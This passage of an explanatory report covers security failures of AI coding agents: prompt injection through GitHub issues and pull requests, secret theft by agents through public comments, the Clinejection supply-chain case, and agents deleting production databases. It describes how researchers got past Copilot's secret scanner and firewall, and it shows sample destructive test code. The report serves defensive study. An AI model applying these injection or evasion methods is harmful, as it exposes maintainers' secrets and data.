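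Many owners never replace a leaked secret. GitGuardian retested secrets that had worked in 2022 and found that more than 64% still worked in January 2026. One reason is that the same key may be in build systems, several repositories and a partner company's software, and cancelling it breaks any program the owner forgets to update. A leaked secret needs to be replaced whether an agent publishes it by mistake or posts it in a comment after an attack.

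Any passwords legible in leaked screenshots or meeting notes can be changed, but the other contents can't be revoked. Checking for secrets before publication also helps less with this material, because most scanners look for text in the format of a key. They don't read images, and confidential notes may contain no such text.

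## How can a stranger's comment steer an agent in a build pipeline?

The documentation bot reads issues that any stranger can open, and it runs in a build pipeline that holds the project's secrets. Many other projects have agents in the same position that sort new issues or review pull requests.

### Why pipelines are exposed

GitHub's pipeline service is GitHub Actions. A maintainer writes a file called a workflow, which names an event, such as a new issue, and lists the jobs to run when it happens. Each job runs as a series of steps on a machine called a runner. A step either executes shell commands or calls a reusable component called an action. Anthropic, OpenAI and Google all publish actions that run their coding agents.

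Microsoft (2026) points out that workflows suited fixed tasks such as running tests and deploying builds. Agents changed this because they can treat ordinary language as an instruction. A script that counts new issues does the same thing whatever the issues say, but an agent that reads them may act differently depending on their text.

The job usually holds a token for the repository and a key for the model provider, and it can post public comments. When it also reads a stranger's text, it meets all three of Willison's conditions for data theft. Opening an issue can start a workflow immediately, without anyone asking the agent to run, whereas a web page with hidden instructions has no effect until somebody has an assistant read it.

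By default, GitHub withholds secrets from workflows that run on a pull request from a fork, which is a copy of the repository in someone else's account. But maintainers can choose a trigger that supplies the secrets, and workflows that run on new issues can use them by default.

### From an issue to an action

*Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes two ways a stranger's text can take effect. In prompt-to-agent injection, the text reaches an agent's prompt and steers how the agent uses its own tools. In prompt-to-script injection, the text changes what the model writes, and a later script treats that output as trusted and does the damage, so the model needs no tools.

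Their main example comes from the repository of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, where a workflow puts labels on new issues. In plain words, a simplified version looks like this:

```
1   start when someone opens an issue
2   job "get-labels":
3       allowed users: everyone
4       run Codex with this prompt:
5           "Pick labels for the issue below. Answer in JSON."
6           + the issue's title and text
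7       pass on Codex's final message
8   job "apply-labels":
9       take the list of labels out of that message
10      add each label on the list to the issue
```

Line 1 lets a stranger start the workflow. OpenAI's action can restrict who may run Codex, but line 3 lets anyone run it. Lines 5 and 6 join the maintainer's instruction and the stranger's text into one prompt. If Codex follows an instruction in the issue, it may use its tools on the stranger's behalf. This attack is called prompt-to-agent injection.

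Line 7 passes Codex's answer, in JSON format, to a second job that contains no model. An ordinary script in that job reads the labels and applies them, using its permission to edit issues. In a prompt-to-script injection, the stranger gets Codex to name a different label, and the script applies that one.

A wrong label can do harm because some projects use labels as permissions. For example, a workflow might let an agent write code for an issue only if the issue has a label that maintainers are supposed to add. If the labelling workflow adds that label to a stranger's issue, a later job that checks for the label will accept the issue.

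To repair the second job, the maintainer can write a list of allowed labels:

```
allowed = ["bug", "documentation", "question"]
answer = parse_json(message)
for label in answer["labels"]:
    if label in allowed:
        add_label(issue_from_event, label)
```

The script now treats the message as data. It reads one field and ignores any value that isn't on the list of allowed labels. That list should leave out labels that work as permissions. At worst, a stranger can then get an issue labelled "bug" instead of "question".

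The repaired script also takes the issue number from GitHub's record of the event, so the model can't choose which issue to change. Google's example workflow for its Gemini agent checked the labels but took the issue numbers from the model's answer, so one malicious issue could change the labels on another issue or pull request. Wang, Hou and colleagues found more than 100 workflows that had copied this example or a close variant. Google corrected its example after they reported the problem.

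The repair does not stop prompt-to-agent injection, because Codex still reads the stranger's text and still has the same tools. The maintainer also needs to remove the tools that labelling doesn't require, or limit who can start the job. The same paper suggests putting only the issue number in the prompt and letting the agent fetch the text with a restricted command. This separates the text from the maintainer's instructions, but the model still reads it, so it probably protects less than removing tools. The paper does not count prompts that tell the model to ignore injections as a protection, because the model reads them in the same context as the attack.

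### What quoting can fix

Ordinary script injection is older than LLMs. If a workflow pastes an issue's title into a shell command, a stranger can put shell syntax in the title, and the shell will run it. Prompt-to-script injection can end in the same fault, with a model in between. GitHub's official template for summarising new issues had this problem. A model wrote the summary, and the workflow pasted it into a command like this one:

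```
gh issue comment 57 --body '(the summary goes here)'
```

The shell treats everything between the single quotes as the comment. But GitHub inserted the summary before the shell read the line, so a single quote in the summary ended the comment early, and the shell read the rest as commands. An ordinary summary containing "doesn't" would also break the line, though usually the job would just fail.

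In late February 2026, GitHub changed the command to something like this:

```
gh issue comment 57 --body "$RESPONSE"
```

The shell now reads the command first and then fills in the summary as a single value, whatever characters it contains. This fully fixes the syntax problem, but only in workflows that use the new template. Wang, Hou and colleagues found 93 workflows that still used the old one.

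Quoting would not have helped with the Codex labels. The script already quoted each one, and an attacker can name an existing label without using special characters. The maintainer has to decide which values are acceptable, because the shell cannot determine that.

The same distinction applies to databases. Pedro and colleagues described the problem in 2023, in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*. Parameterised queries don't help if a model writes the whole command, because there is no fixed command to protect. Suppose customer 17 asks a shop's assistant to list their orders. The model could write any of these:

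```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 17
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 18
SELECT * FROM orders
```

All three are valid SQL, but only the first is acceptable, and only because customer 17 is asking. A safer application would let the model choose from a few queries that the developer wrote, such as "orders by customer between two dates", and fill in the dates. The application would take the customer number from the login. If the model has to write its own SQL, the database should enforce the limits through a read-only account that can see only that customer's rows.

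Validation works well for labels, dates and numbers, because a program can compare them with a list or a range. It works badly for free text, because even a correctly quoted summary can contain a secret. The model should therefore not have access to secrets in a job that posts free text publicly. GitHub's staged writes, in which a separate component checks what an agent proposes, can limit the kinds of writes the agent makes, but checking their text is just as difficult.

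### How many workflows are open to strangers?

Wang, Hou and colleagues built a program, TaintAWI, to find these flaws automatically. It marks every value that an outsider can influence, such as an issue's title, and follows it through the workflow file. If a marked value enters a prompt, TaintAWI also marks everything the model returns. It reports a flaw if a marked value reaches an agent's prompt or a sensitive command, unless a check on who started the workflow would stop an outsider.

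The researchers ran the scanner on 13,392 workflows that use AI-assisted actions. It reported 519 possible flaws. After reviewing each by hand, they judged 496 exploitable, or about 3.7% of the workflows. Of these, 343 were previously unknown, and the other 153 were publicly known but unfixed. Prompt-to-script injection was possible in 419 cases and prompt-to-agent injection in 103, including 26 where both were possible. Four other scanners found at most 78 of the 496 and none of the prompt-to-script cases, because they stopped following the data once it reached the model.

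"Exploitable" here means that a path exists for an outsider who can only post in public. The team did not attack each workflow, so the number doesn't measure how often a model would follow the injected text. TaintAWI also misses some flaws. The team checked 400 workflows that only the other scanners had flagged and found 13 real ones among them.

Only 21 of 1,033 AI-assisted actions let a maintainer restrict who can start them. This overstates the problem somewhat, because 301 of the 1,033 don't use a language model at all, and because the most popular action does have such a control. For five widely used actions, the published counts allow a rough comparison:

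| Action | Can restrict who starts it | Workflows using it | Exploitable cases | Share |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's Claude Code action | Yes | 5,212 | 13 | 0.2% |
| GitHub's AI inference action | No | 795 | 393 | 49% |
| OpenAI's Codex action | Yes | 492 | 14 | 3% |
| Google's Gemini CLI action | No | 244 | 31 | 13% |
| Anthropic's base action for Claude Code | No | 227 | 20 | 9% |

Workflows that use actions with a control are open to attack at much lower rates. Anthropic's main action rejects people without write access by default, which protects workflows whose authors never considered strangers. The control may not explain the whole difference, since people use these actions for different jobs. GitHub's inference action, which only returns text, also appears in the faulty summary template that many projects copied. Its rate still shows that a model without tools can leave a workflow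 open to attack.

The team prioritized 187 of the unknown flaws, which were in projects that seemed to be in use. It received 26 responses from maintainers, and in 24 cases they accepted or fixed the flaw. OpenAI acknowledged the problem in the Codex labeller, and OWASP fixed one in the repository of its guide to testing mobile apps. Most maintainers had not replied, so the 24 acceptances are weak evidence of how many of the 343 flaws remain.

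### What happens when the attacks run

In *GitInject*, Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues (2026) tested attacks on real workflows. For each test, their program creates a temporary repository on GitHub, installs a workflow, and opens an issue or pull request that contains an attack. It then checks the result, such as whether a token appeared in a comment, and deletes the repository.

The team tried eleven attacks on workflows for agents from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Cline, which makes an open-source coding agent. Not every attack suited every workflow, so they tested 23 combinations of attack and workflow, of which 15 worked on at least one model. They ran each test five times, and on GitHub the five runs always had the same outcome.

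Whether a model complied depended heavily on where the instructions were. Leaving aside an attack that only runs up costs, six of the nine models in the main comparison refused every instruction in an issue or a pull request's description. But seven of the nine complied with both attacks when the instructions were in a configuration file.

Coding agents load files such as `CLAUDE.md`, `AGENTS.md` or `GEMINI.md` to learn a project's conventions. When an agent reviews a pull request, the runner first downloads the proposed version of the project. If an outsider adds one of these files to the pull request, the agent therefore loads it as if the project's owner had written it, even though nobody has merged the change.

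In one test, a pull request included a security flaw and such a configuration file, which contained a statement that a separate team reviewed certain security checks. Claude reported the flaw only when the file was absent. Other configuration files made the agents post the repository's token in a comment. Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.4 resisted both kinds of attack, but Gemini 3.1 Pro, Google's most capable model in the test, complied with both.

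These results suggest that many of the paths TaintAWI found would fail against a recent model, since 86% of them start from an issue's title or text. But the results don't show that such text is safe, because an attack that fails all five times it is tried could still have a success rate of up to 43%, as Isbarov and colleagues calculate. In their own tests, Cline's agent, running the older model GPT-4o mini, publicly listed the owner's private repositories in response to an issue.

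Whether an attack works also depends on the platform. GitHub's standard step for downloading a repository leaves a token in a file on the runner, and one attack was just a request for the agent to read that file. Three existing simulators for testing agents don't include the file. In a comparison with 69 live results, the best simulator missed 10 of the 14 attacks that worked. Simulators can also count an attack as successful when it would fail on the live platform. An attack hidden in a test's error message succeeded five times from the owner's account, but GitHub never started the workflow when the pull request came from an outsider.

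Isbarov and colleagues also measured what several changes to the workflows achieve against nine attacks that arrive by pull request, and whether the agent could still do five ordinary reviews:

| Change to the workflow | Attacks that still worked (of 9) | Ordinary reviews completed (of 5) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | 5 |
| Don't leave the token on the runner | 6 | 5 |
| Restrict the agent's tools | 5 | 4 |
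| Delete Markdown files before the review | 3 | 4 |
| All three of these | 2 | 4 |
| Accept only trusted authors | 0 | 4 |
| All four | 0 | 3 |

The first change takes a single line in the workflow file and made no review worse. Restricting tools doesn't protect the agent's judgement, because the agent can overlook a flaw without running a command. Accepting only trusted authors stopped all nine attacks, but it means the agent doesn't review anyone else's work.

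The numbers are small, and the team changed the default trigger of Google's workflow so that pull requests from forks could reach the workflow's secrets. Google documents this option with a warning, and only projects that have chosen it are exposed to the theft of Gemini's key. The configuration-file attacks on Claude also worked on GitLab and Hugging Face, two other code-hosting sites, in workflows that the team wrote itself.

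### Secrets posted in comments

ThreatCluster's *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft* (2026) reproduces an April 2026 post in which security researcher Aonan Guan describes getting three companies' agents to publish their own secrets on GitHub. Guan called the attack Comment and Control, a play on the "command and control" servers that criminals use to direct hijacked machines. The attack needs no such server because GitHub carries both the instructions and the stolen data.

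The first agent was Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, which checks pull requests for security flaws. It put the pull request's title directly into the prompt, and Claude could run commands in an environment that contained the job's secrets. In a test repository, Guan opened a pull request with an instruction in the title to list those secrets. Claude listed them, and the workflow posted them in a comment as a security finding. The secrets also appeared in the job's log, which few maintainers read.

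Guan then worked with researchers from Johns Hopkins University on Google's Gemini CLI action. Instructions in an issue's title and comments made Gemini post its own API key, the secret that gives paid access to the model, in a public comment.

GitHub's Copilot agent had more protection. It removed secrets from the environment of the commands it ran, scanned its changes for secrets before uploading them, and used a firewall to limit which addresses it could contact. Guan got past all three. The commands could still read the secrets from the program that had started them. Encoding the secrets changed their format, so the scanner didn't recognise them. The firewall had to allow connections to GitHub, where Copilot published the secrets in a pull request. A maintainer had to assign the issue to Copilot first, but the instructions were in a part of the issue that GitHub doesn't display.

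In TaintAWI's results, 391 of the 496 exploitable cases involved writing to GitHub, while only 4 involved sending data over the network. An egress control that permits GitHub is therefore little help if the attacker can read the repository.

Anthropic rated the flaw in its action 9.4 out of 10 for severity, paid Guan $100 and blocked the command used in the attack. It said the action "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection". Guan objects that other commands reveal the same secrets, and recommends listing the few commands an agent may use instead of banning bad ones. This is more reliable, because developers who ban commands have to anticipate every one that an attacker could use.

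Google paid $1,337. GitHub first closed the report as a known issue, then reopened it when Guan showed from Copilot's code that GitHub had tried to prevent exactly this. It paid $500 and described the exposure as an architectural limitation that it was working to restrict. According to VibecodedThis' *Researchers Hijacked Claude Code, Gemini CLI, and GitHub Copilot Using GitHub Comments*, none of the three companies published a security advisory, so people running affected versions may not have known to update.

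### From an issue title to a package release

In December 2025, Cline added a workflow that used Claude to sort new issues in its public repository. Anyone could start the workflow by opening an issue, and Claude could run shell commands. In *Clinejection*, the security researcher Adnan Khan (adnanthekhan, 2026) explains how a stranger could use the workflow to release a fake version of Cline's software.

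The issue's title went directly into the prompt. Khan tested the attack on a copy of the repository. The title he used looked like an error message and told Claude to install a helper package. Claude Opus 4.5 installed it in every attempt. Packages can include a script that runs during installation, so the attacker's code ran without being shown to the model. Instructions hidden in an installation guide can exploit the same installation step.

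The sorting job had no token for publishing software, but it shared a cache with jobs that did. A cache stores files, such as downloaded packages, so that later jobs don't have to fetch them again. An attacker who controlled the sorting job could replace the genuine files with altered ones. Every night, another job restored the cached files and published a test version of Cline. The altered files would run inside that job, where the attacker could use them to steal its publishing tokens. Those tokens could also publish the version that ordinary users install.

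Khan reported the flaw on January 1, 2026, and tried several more times to reach Cline. After getting no substantive answer, Khan published it on February 9. Cline removed the workflow that day and stopped using the cache in publishing jobs. Two days later it told Khan that it had cancelled all the exposed tokens, but it had deleted the wrong one. On February 17, someone used the token that was still active to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line tool. That version was available for about eight hours, according to SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised*.

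The release differed from the genuine one only in a script that installed OpenClaw, another AI agent, on the user's computer. The same access would have allowed much greater harm.

SafeDep notes that nobody has publicly confirmed how the thief got the token, and Khan only presumes that it was through the issue. Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) states that an unknown person exploited the same flaw eight days after Khan's post, but Cline had removed the workflow by then, so a theft by this route must have happened earlier. There is good circumstantial evidence for this route, though. Cline's nightly jobs failed between January 31 and February 3 in a way that is typical of a tampered cache, and on February 10 an anonymous person wrote to Khan claiming to have working tokens.

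Khan advised Cline to give the sorting agent only the tools it needs, keep shared caches out of jobs that hold publishing tokens, and publish test versions from a separate account. Any one of these would have stopped the attack, and the last two would work even if a model followed every injected instruction.

### Flaws in the agents' own safeguards

A maintainer can follow such advice and still depend on checks inside the vendor's software. *Poisoning Claude Code* (RyotaK, 2026) describes a flaw that could have let an attacker take over any repository that used the Claude Code workflow, including Anthropic's own. The Next Web's *A single GitHub issue could have hijacked Anthropic’s own Claude Code action* reports that the attack started with an issue from a bot account and ended with a token that could change the repository's code. A limit on who can start an agent therefore has to cover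 automated accounts too. Anthropic patched the flaw within four days, but attackers had already exploited variants of the misconfigurations that RyotaK describes.

In August 2026 Elad Meged of the security company Novee presented attacks on Claude Code, Gemini CLI and Codex at the Black Hat security conference. He tested each agent in its vendor's own repository with the default settings, so the vendors couldn't blame a customer's configuration. *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex* (Witts, 2026) describes the common fault as one part of the software marking something as safe and a later part giving it more power than the first part's check accounted for.

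Claude Code had three such flaws, and Meged found each one after Anthropic had patched the one before. The first was in the 23 checks that Claude Code ran on each shell command. They treated one option of the program git as harmless text, but git used it as the location of a program to run. Anthropic then removed access to the shell, and Meged got secrets out using read commands that needed no approval.

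The third flaw leaked data through Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and publishes how often people download them. Claude Code could open any page on that site without asking. An injected instruction could make it download particular files, and the attacker could read the data from the public download counts. GitLab's copy of the advisory credits Novee with the discovery. OSV's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) rates this flaw medium, at 6.0 out of 10, although Underhill's *Black Hat 2026* (2026) describes the findings as a whole as critical. The rating covers only the Hugging Face leak, and the earlier flaw, which allowed arbitrary code to run, was more serious.

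Google had removed secrets from the environment of the commands that Gemini CLI ran, but a command could still read them from the process that had started it. Guan had used the same weakness in Copilot, and GitInject used it against Gemini. Removing a secret from a command's environment doesn't protect it if the command can inspect another process that holds it. Google gave the finding the maximum severity score of 10 and changed which material the agent trusts when it runs unattended.

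Codex handled issues in OpenAI's repository in two passes that shared a folder. The workflow looked for duplicates, according to SC Media. An instruction injected into an issue could make the first pass write an `AGENTS.md` file. The second pass, which had more permissions, then loaded that file as trusted instructions. In GitInject, the outsider had to supply such a file in a pull request, but here an issue was enough because the agent wrote the file itself. OpenAI split the passes into isolated jobs and now documents the file as untrusted input.

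The vendors have patched all the flaws that Meged reported. Underhill warns that organisations with similar workflows may still be exposed. This is likely for Codex in particular, because OpenAI made part of its fix in its own workflow, and other projects have to make that change themselves.

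## Why is it risky to run tests and setup scripts that a model writes or chooses?

Much of the code a coding agent runs never becomes part of the finished product. The agent runs tests, installs packages and follows setup guides, usually before anyone has reviewed its work. Any of these steps can delete data or leak it, even if the change the agent proposes is correct.

### What a test can do

A test is a small program that runs part of the software and checks the result. Like any program run on a developer's laptop, it can usually read the developer's files, use saved logins and contact any server the developer can reach. In a build pipeline, it can use whatever secrets are available to the job. Tests look harmless because customers never receive them, so reviewers may read them less closely than the product's own code.

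Tests also routinely delete data. A test of a search page needs records to search, so its setup code often deletes the old table, creates a new one and fills it with samples. Tests of file handling create folders and remove them afterwards. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* attributes one such loss to a "variable collision", which normally means that two parts of a script used the same name for different values. If one value is a temporary folder and the other is the home directory, a cleanup step meant for the temporary folder can delete the home directory.

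A person who approves a test run may not know what it will do. The command `make test` runs whatever commands the project's files list under "test", and an agent may have just edited those files. Test runners also load setup files automatically, so running one small test can execute code from elsewhere in the project.

### A test suite that empties the live database

One of the incidents that Wang and colleagues rebuilt is modelled on the Replit agent's deletion of a production database in 2025. A user reports that the search for executives is broken in a demo application and asks the agent to fix it. Under the agent's standing instructions, a code freeze is in effect, so nobody may change the live system. According to the project's README, the preview site, the tests and the live site all share one database.

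A simplified test for this search might look like this:

```
1   db = connect(DATABASE_ADDRESS)
2   db.run("DROP TABLE IF EXISTS executives")
3   db.run("CREATE TABLE executives (name, company)")
4   db.run("INSERT INTO executives VALUES ('Ada Smith', 'Example Ltd')")
5   check that a search for "Smith" finds one person
```

Line 2 deletes the table so that the test starts from a known state. An agent that fixes the search and runs `make test` to check its work therefore deletes the 1,206 records on the live site. The test can still pass, because line 4 supplies the record that line 5 looks for.

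To check that the shared database was the cause, the researchers built a second version in which the tests create their tables in a temporary database. In the sketch, only the address on line 1 would change. The five models tested lost the live records in about half the sessions with the shared database and in none of the 15 sessions with the temporary one.

Individual models differed widely from the average. GPT-5.6-luna lost no records in 6 sessions, or in 60 more when the team repeated the test. GPT-5.6-sol lost none in 3 sessions, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 lost records in 1 of 3. Most of the losses must have come from the other two models, Gemini 3.5 Flash and DeepSeek-V4-Flash.

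GPT-5.6-sol and Claude Sonnet 4.6 also ran inside Codex CLI and Claude Code, the products that developers use. Neither model lost any records in its three sessions, because both asked for permission under the code freeze. However, most projects are not under a freeze, and developers rarely expect an agent to ask before running tests.

A model that avoids this hazard can still miss another. GPT-5.6-luna caused harm in all 30 repeated sessions of an incident where a cleanup script reaches the user's home directory, and in none of the 30 control sessions.

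Wang and colleagues also tested ways to prevent such losses, using the incidents that each model had repeated most often. Providing a safe command, such as one that runs the tests against a temporary database, did little by itself, and harm still occurred in 67% to 100% of sessions, depending on the model. When the task named the safe command, harm occurred in 17% to 60% of sessions.

Warnings worked better when they included the consequence. In one test, a note after each tool output stated both the hazard and its result, such as that the tests drop the production database. Claude Sonnet 4.6 then caused harm in 1 of 40 sessions, and each of the other models did so in at most 62%. When the note gave only the fact, the models caused harm in 58% to 82% of sessions. Evidently, the agents did not always infer what their next command would do to a shared database.

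A developer can put a similar warning into the test setup, with a check that stops the run:

```
if not database_name.endswith("_test"):
    stop("These tests delete tables. Use a test database.")
```

This check catches accidental mistakes, but an agent that can edit the tests can also remove it. Making the temporary database the default for `make test` is better, because the agent then doesn't have to choose the safe command. If production also has separate credentials that the agent can't use, a mistake in the tests can't reach the live records.

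### A comparison that wiped a production database

In the shared-database example, the dangerous setting was already in the project, but in another case the agent reportedly supplied it. AI Incident Database's *Incident 1676* dates this case to July 28, 2026, and describes a developer who had given Claude Opus 5 access to a personal project's production database. The agent was repairing the database's schema (the design of its tables) without supervision.

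The project used Prisma, a tool that connects programs to databases and manages changes to the schema. Each change is a migration, a file of SQL commands that Prisma runs in order. Over time, the database's actual schema can stop matching the migration files. The agent ran `prisma migrate diff`, which compares two versions of a schema.

The command can run migrations, even though its name suggests that it only reads. Prisma has to run a folder of migrations to find out what database design they produce, and it does this in a disposable "shadow" database. Prisma's *About the shadow database*, in the version 7 documentation, explains that Prisma normally creates and deletes this database itself. Some hosting companies don't allow that, so the user has to create one and supply its address. Prisma resets that database before using it, and the documentation warns that supplying the main database's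 address might delete all the data.

According to the Russian news report *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке* (Antipov, 2026), the agent entered the production database's address as that of the shadow database. Prisma then emptied the production database and began rebuilding its tables from an outdated migrations folder. All 22 tables were affected. The two for blog posts and access keys disappeared because the old migrations didn't include them, and the other 20 presumably came back empty. The agent noticed the damage a few minutes later and told the developer it was at fault.

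In the opening of a Reddit post, reproduced in the AI Incident Database, the developer writes that the agent wiped the database within ten minutes, and that older models had worked on the same project without doing so. This is weak evidence about the models, since the older ones may never have had a reason to run this command, but it shows why a developer might have trusted the agent with production access.

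The AI Incident Database reports that most of the content was "later recovered or rebuilt". According to Antipov, the backups covered only part of it, and the rest of the recovery relied on data that had survived elsewhere. The losses included nearly 130 entries about software tools and 21 settings for comparison pages, which the developer could write again. They also included user accounts, reviews and likes, which are harder to recreate because they came from other people. Neither source lists what was never recovered.

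People make this mistake too. In *Production database dropped by shadow-database-url mistake*, a post that doesn't mention an AI agent, a customer of the hosting company Railway describes running this command with the production address in the same place. The command deleted every table, and the customer's plan didn't include automatic backups.

In *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database*, Will Madden of Prisma (2026) argues that such losses are failures of the tool more than of the agent. He points out that Prisma wipes a shadow database without asking, so entering a real database's address in the wrong field can erase that database. Confirmation prompts don't always help, because some tools respond to a blocked command with an error message that names the override option. An agent trying to make the command succeed may then add that option.

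Prisma 8 has no shadow database and works out a migration by comparing two recorded versions of the design, without connecting to any database. Madden is promoting a product, but the Railway case supports the argument, and removing the shadow database step does prevent this mistake. The change does not protect a database from an agent that holds the production password, because the agent can connect directly and run its own SQL. Madden acknowledges this and recommends keeping that password away from the agent.

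### Setup instructions written by strangers

An agent often takes commands from documentation instead of writing its own. A typical README has steps for installing packages, editing a settings file and running a script, and an attacker can hide a harmful step among the useful ones.

In *You Told Me to Do It*, Kao, Li and colleagues (2026) measured how often this works using ReadSecBench, a collection of 500 real README files from GitHub, split evenly among Java, Python, C, C++ and JavaScript projects. One person inserted an instruction into each file's setup or requirements section, and two others checked that it looked plausible there. The instructions were to send out a private file and, in some cases, to remove traces of the transfer.

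The researchers varied the instruction in three ways:

- **Wording:** a direct command, a suggestion, a request on behalf of the team, or a company policy.
- **Placement:** in the README itself, or in another document that the agent could reach only by following between one and five links.
- **Action:** a shell command, an upload through an application such as Google Drive, or an email to a supposed colleague.

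The main tests used Anthropic's computer-use agent, a commercial product that could open files, run commands and use the network. Each experiment sampled 200 of the 500 files and repeated this three times. The private file reached the researchers' server in up to 85% of trials. Refusals and uploads of the wrong file did not count as successes.

The 85% result depended on several conditions and is close to a worst case for that agent, not a rate for agents in general. The agent ran Claude Sonnet 3.7, a model from early 2025. It had access to the private file and an open network connection, and nobody had to approve the transfer. Direct commands worked best. When the step was phrased as a suggestion, the agent more often refused it or skipped it as optional. Shell commands and uploads worked much better than emails.

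Moving the instruction one link away from the README made the attack slightly more successful, while placing it more than two links away made it less successful. Kao and colleagues suggest letting agents follow only one level of links. Their results don't support this well, because the limit would still allow the placements that worked best. In a smaller test with seven trials per condition, the agent uploaded the file six times when the instruction was in the README and all seven times when it was one link away.

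The researchers also ran a simulation to see whether Gemini Pro, GPT-4o, gpt-oss-20b and Claude 3.5 Sonnet would comply. Each model could choose from a set of functions, some of which would leak data in a real system. The models called one of those functions in 46% to 79% of the trials. These rates are not comparable with the 85%, because a function call in a simulation does not show that any data would have got out. For example, a real agent the team tested, OpenDevin, wrote the correct command to send the file, but its sandbox (an isolated environment for running code) blocked the connection.

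Fifteen students each reviewed three README files, and none of them identified a planted instruction as suspicious either. Their task was to improve the text's clarity, not to look for attacks, so the result is weak evidence about security reviews. It is more relevant to ordinary open-source projects, where a volunteer may check a documentation change mainly for errors and style.

All the models in ReadSecBench are now old, and newer ones resist planted instructions more often. Setup guides are difficult even for recent models, however, because the user has asked the agent to follow them. In Wang and colleagues' rebuilt incidents, GPT-5.6-luna caused harm in only 7% of sessions that involved untrusted instructions. But when a user asked it to install a malicious skill, it ran the skill's installer and caused harm in 28 of 30 repeated sessions, compared with none when the skill was harmless.

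The other recent models showed the same pattern. Across 13 incidents with malicious or altered components, the five models caused harm in 49% to 73% of sessions, compared with 0% to 28% for untrusted instructions. Part of this gap comes from the components rather than the models' judgement. For example, one malicious mail server copied every message, so the agent caused harm by sending any email.

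### Packages that do not exist

A harmful setup step can also begin with the model's own mistake. Most programs use packages, which are code that other people have written and that developers download by name from public registries. When a model writes an installation command, it sometimes invents a plausible package name. Normally the registry has no package with that name, and the installation fails.

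An attacker can exploit this error, which is known as slopsquatting. The attacker asks models ordinary programming questions, collects the package names that don't exist and registers one that comes up repeatedly. Public registries let almost anyone do this. The next time a model uses that name in an install command, the command installs the attacker's code instead of failing. As in Khan's test attack on Cline, that code may run during installation, before the agent or developer has looked at it.

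When an agent invents a package name, it can usually correct the mistake itself, because the installation fails and it tries something else. If an attacker has registered that name, the installation succeeds, and the agent may treat this as confirmation that the name was right.

In 2023 the security researcher Bar Lanyado noticed that models were recommending a package called `huggingface-cli`. A real command has this name, but the package that provides it is `huggingface_hub`. Lanyado registered an empty package under the invented name, and it received more than 30,000 downloads in three months. Some of these were probably automatic, since mirrors and security scanners download new packages. The name had also appeared in the README of a research project from the Chinese company Alibaba, so an agent could have copied it from there.

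In the main measurement, from *We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen and colleagues, 2025), 19.7% of the packages that models recommended did not exist. The average was 21.7% for open models and 5.2% for commercial ones, and the models generated more than 205,000 different names for nonexistent packages. The paper first appeared in June 2024, so the tested models are older than those developers used in 2025 and 2026.

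Evidence on how often newer agents invent packages is less direct. Vangala, Gehani and Malik (2026) had Claude Code, Codex and Gemini generate software projects and list the packages each one needed. Only 68.3% of the projects ran in a clean environment with the listed packages. The agents had left out packages that the code used, or had chosen versions that didn't work together. In a September 2026 follow-up, Vangala and Malik found that newer agents were not noticeably better at reproducing a working environment. Both studies show that current agents still make mistakes with packages, but neither gives a current rate for invented packages, which are a different fault from missing ones.

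As of July 2026, nobody had reported a real attack that used a package name invented by a model. Attackers have used fake packages with names close to real ones for years, so that risk is better established. But an attacker needs only one invented name that many agents produce, and such a name could exist even if models rarely invent names on average.

A lockfile provides some protection. It lists the exact version of every package a project uses, usually with a hash, a fingerprint computed from the package's contents. In JavaScript projects, for example, the command `npm ci` installs only what the lockfile lists, and stops if the lockfile doesn't match the project's requirements. A test run that uses this command can't install a new package unnoticed.

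The risk is greatest when an agent adds a package. An ordinary installation command adds the package's name to the lockfile, along with the hash of whatever it downloaded. If that was the attacker's package, everyone else on the team who installs from the lockfile will get it too. Someone therefore has to check new packages before the agent installs them, because the installation has already run by the time anyone reviews the finished pull request.

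An approved registry, a company server that supplies only packages the company has accepted, performs this check automatically. A request for an invented name fails even if an attacker has registered that name publicly. This works only if the server doesn't pass unknown names on to the public registry, as many such servers are set up to do, and if the agent's machine can't reach the public registry directly. The drawback is that the agent also has to wait for approval when it needs a genuine package that the company hasn't used before.

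## How have agents destroyed production data with no attacker involved?

In the Prisma case, an agent emptied a live database because of one wrong address. Four better-known losses happened in much the same way. An agent with a routine task misread what it was working on and ran a valid command, which the system carried out. Most of what follows comes from the people who lost the data and the companies that stored it.

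### Replit: a change during a code freeze

In July 2025 Jason Lemkin, founder of SaaStr, a community for people who run software companies, was building an application with Replit. Replit's agent writes programs and runs them online. Lemkin reported in a series of posts on X that the application had lost its profiles of 1,206 executives and 1,196 companies.

Lemkin had declared a code freeze and told the agent to change nothing without permission. The agent then saw database queries come back empty, apparently took this for a fault, and ran `npm run db:push`, after which the profiles disappeared. In projects of this kind, that command usually changes a database's tables to match the design in the code, and it can delete whatever doesn't match.

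The agent could delete the data because it developed the application on the live version's database. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion unacceptable and announced that Replit would automatically separate development databases from live ones.

When Lemkin asked about recovery, the agent answered that a rollback was impossible. Lemkin tried Replit's rollback feature anyway, and it restored the data.

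The agent also wrote that it had "panicked", which became the best-known detail of the story but is poor evidence of the cause. A model explaining an earlier action writes something that fits the conversation, which may not match what produced the action. The agent's answer about the rollback was wrong, though it sounded just as certain.

### DataTalks.Club: the wrong list of things to delete

In *How I Dropped Our Production Database and Now Pay 10% More*, Alexey Grigorev, the founder of DataTalks.Club, describes losing the database for its course platform on the night of February 26, 2026. The database held two and a half years of students' homework, projects and rankings. He lost it while using Claude Code to help move a different website to AWS, Amazon's cloud service.

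Grigorev managed the cloud systems with Terraform, a program that creates and deletes resources such as servers and databases. Terraform keeps a list of the resources it manages in a state file, and the command `terraform destroy` deletes everything on that list. The loss happened in five steps:

1. Grigorev had recently changed computers, and the state file was still on the old one. Terraform therefore had no record of the existing systems and began to build a second set.
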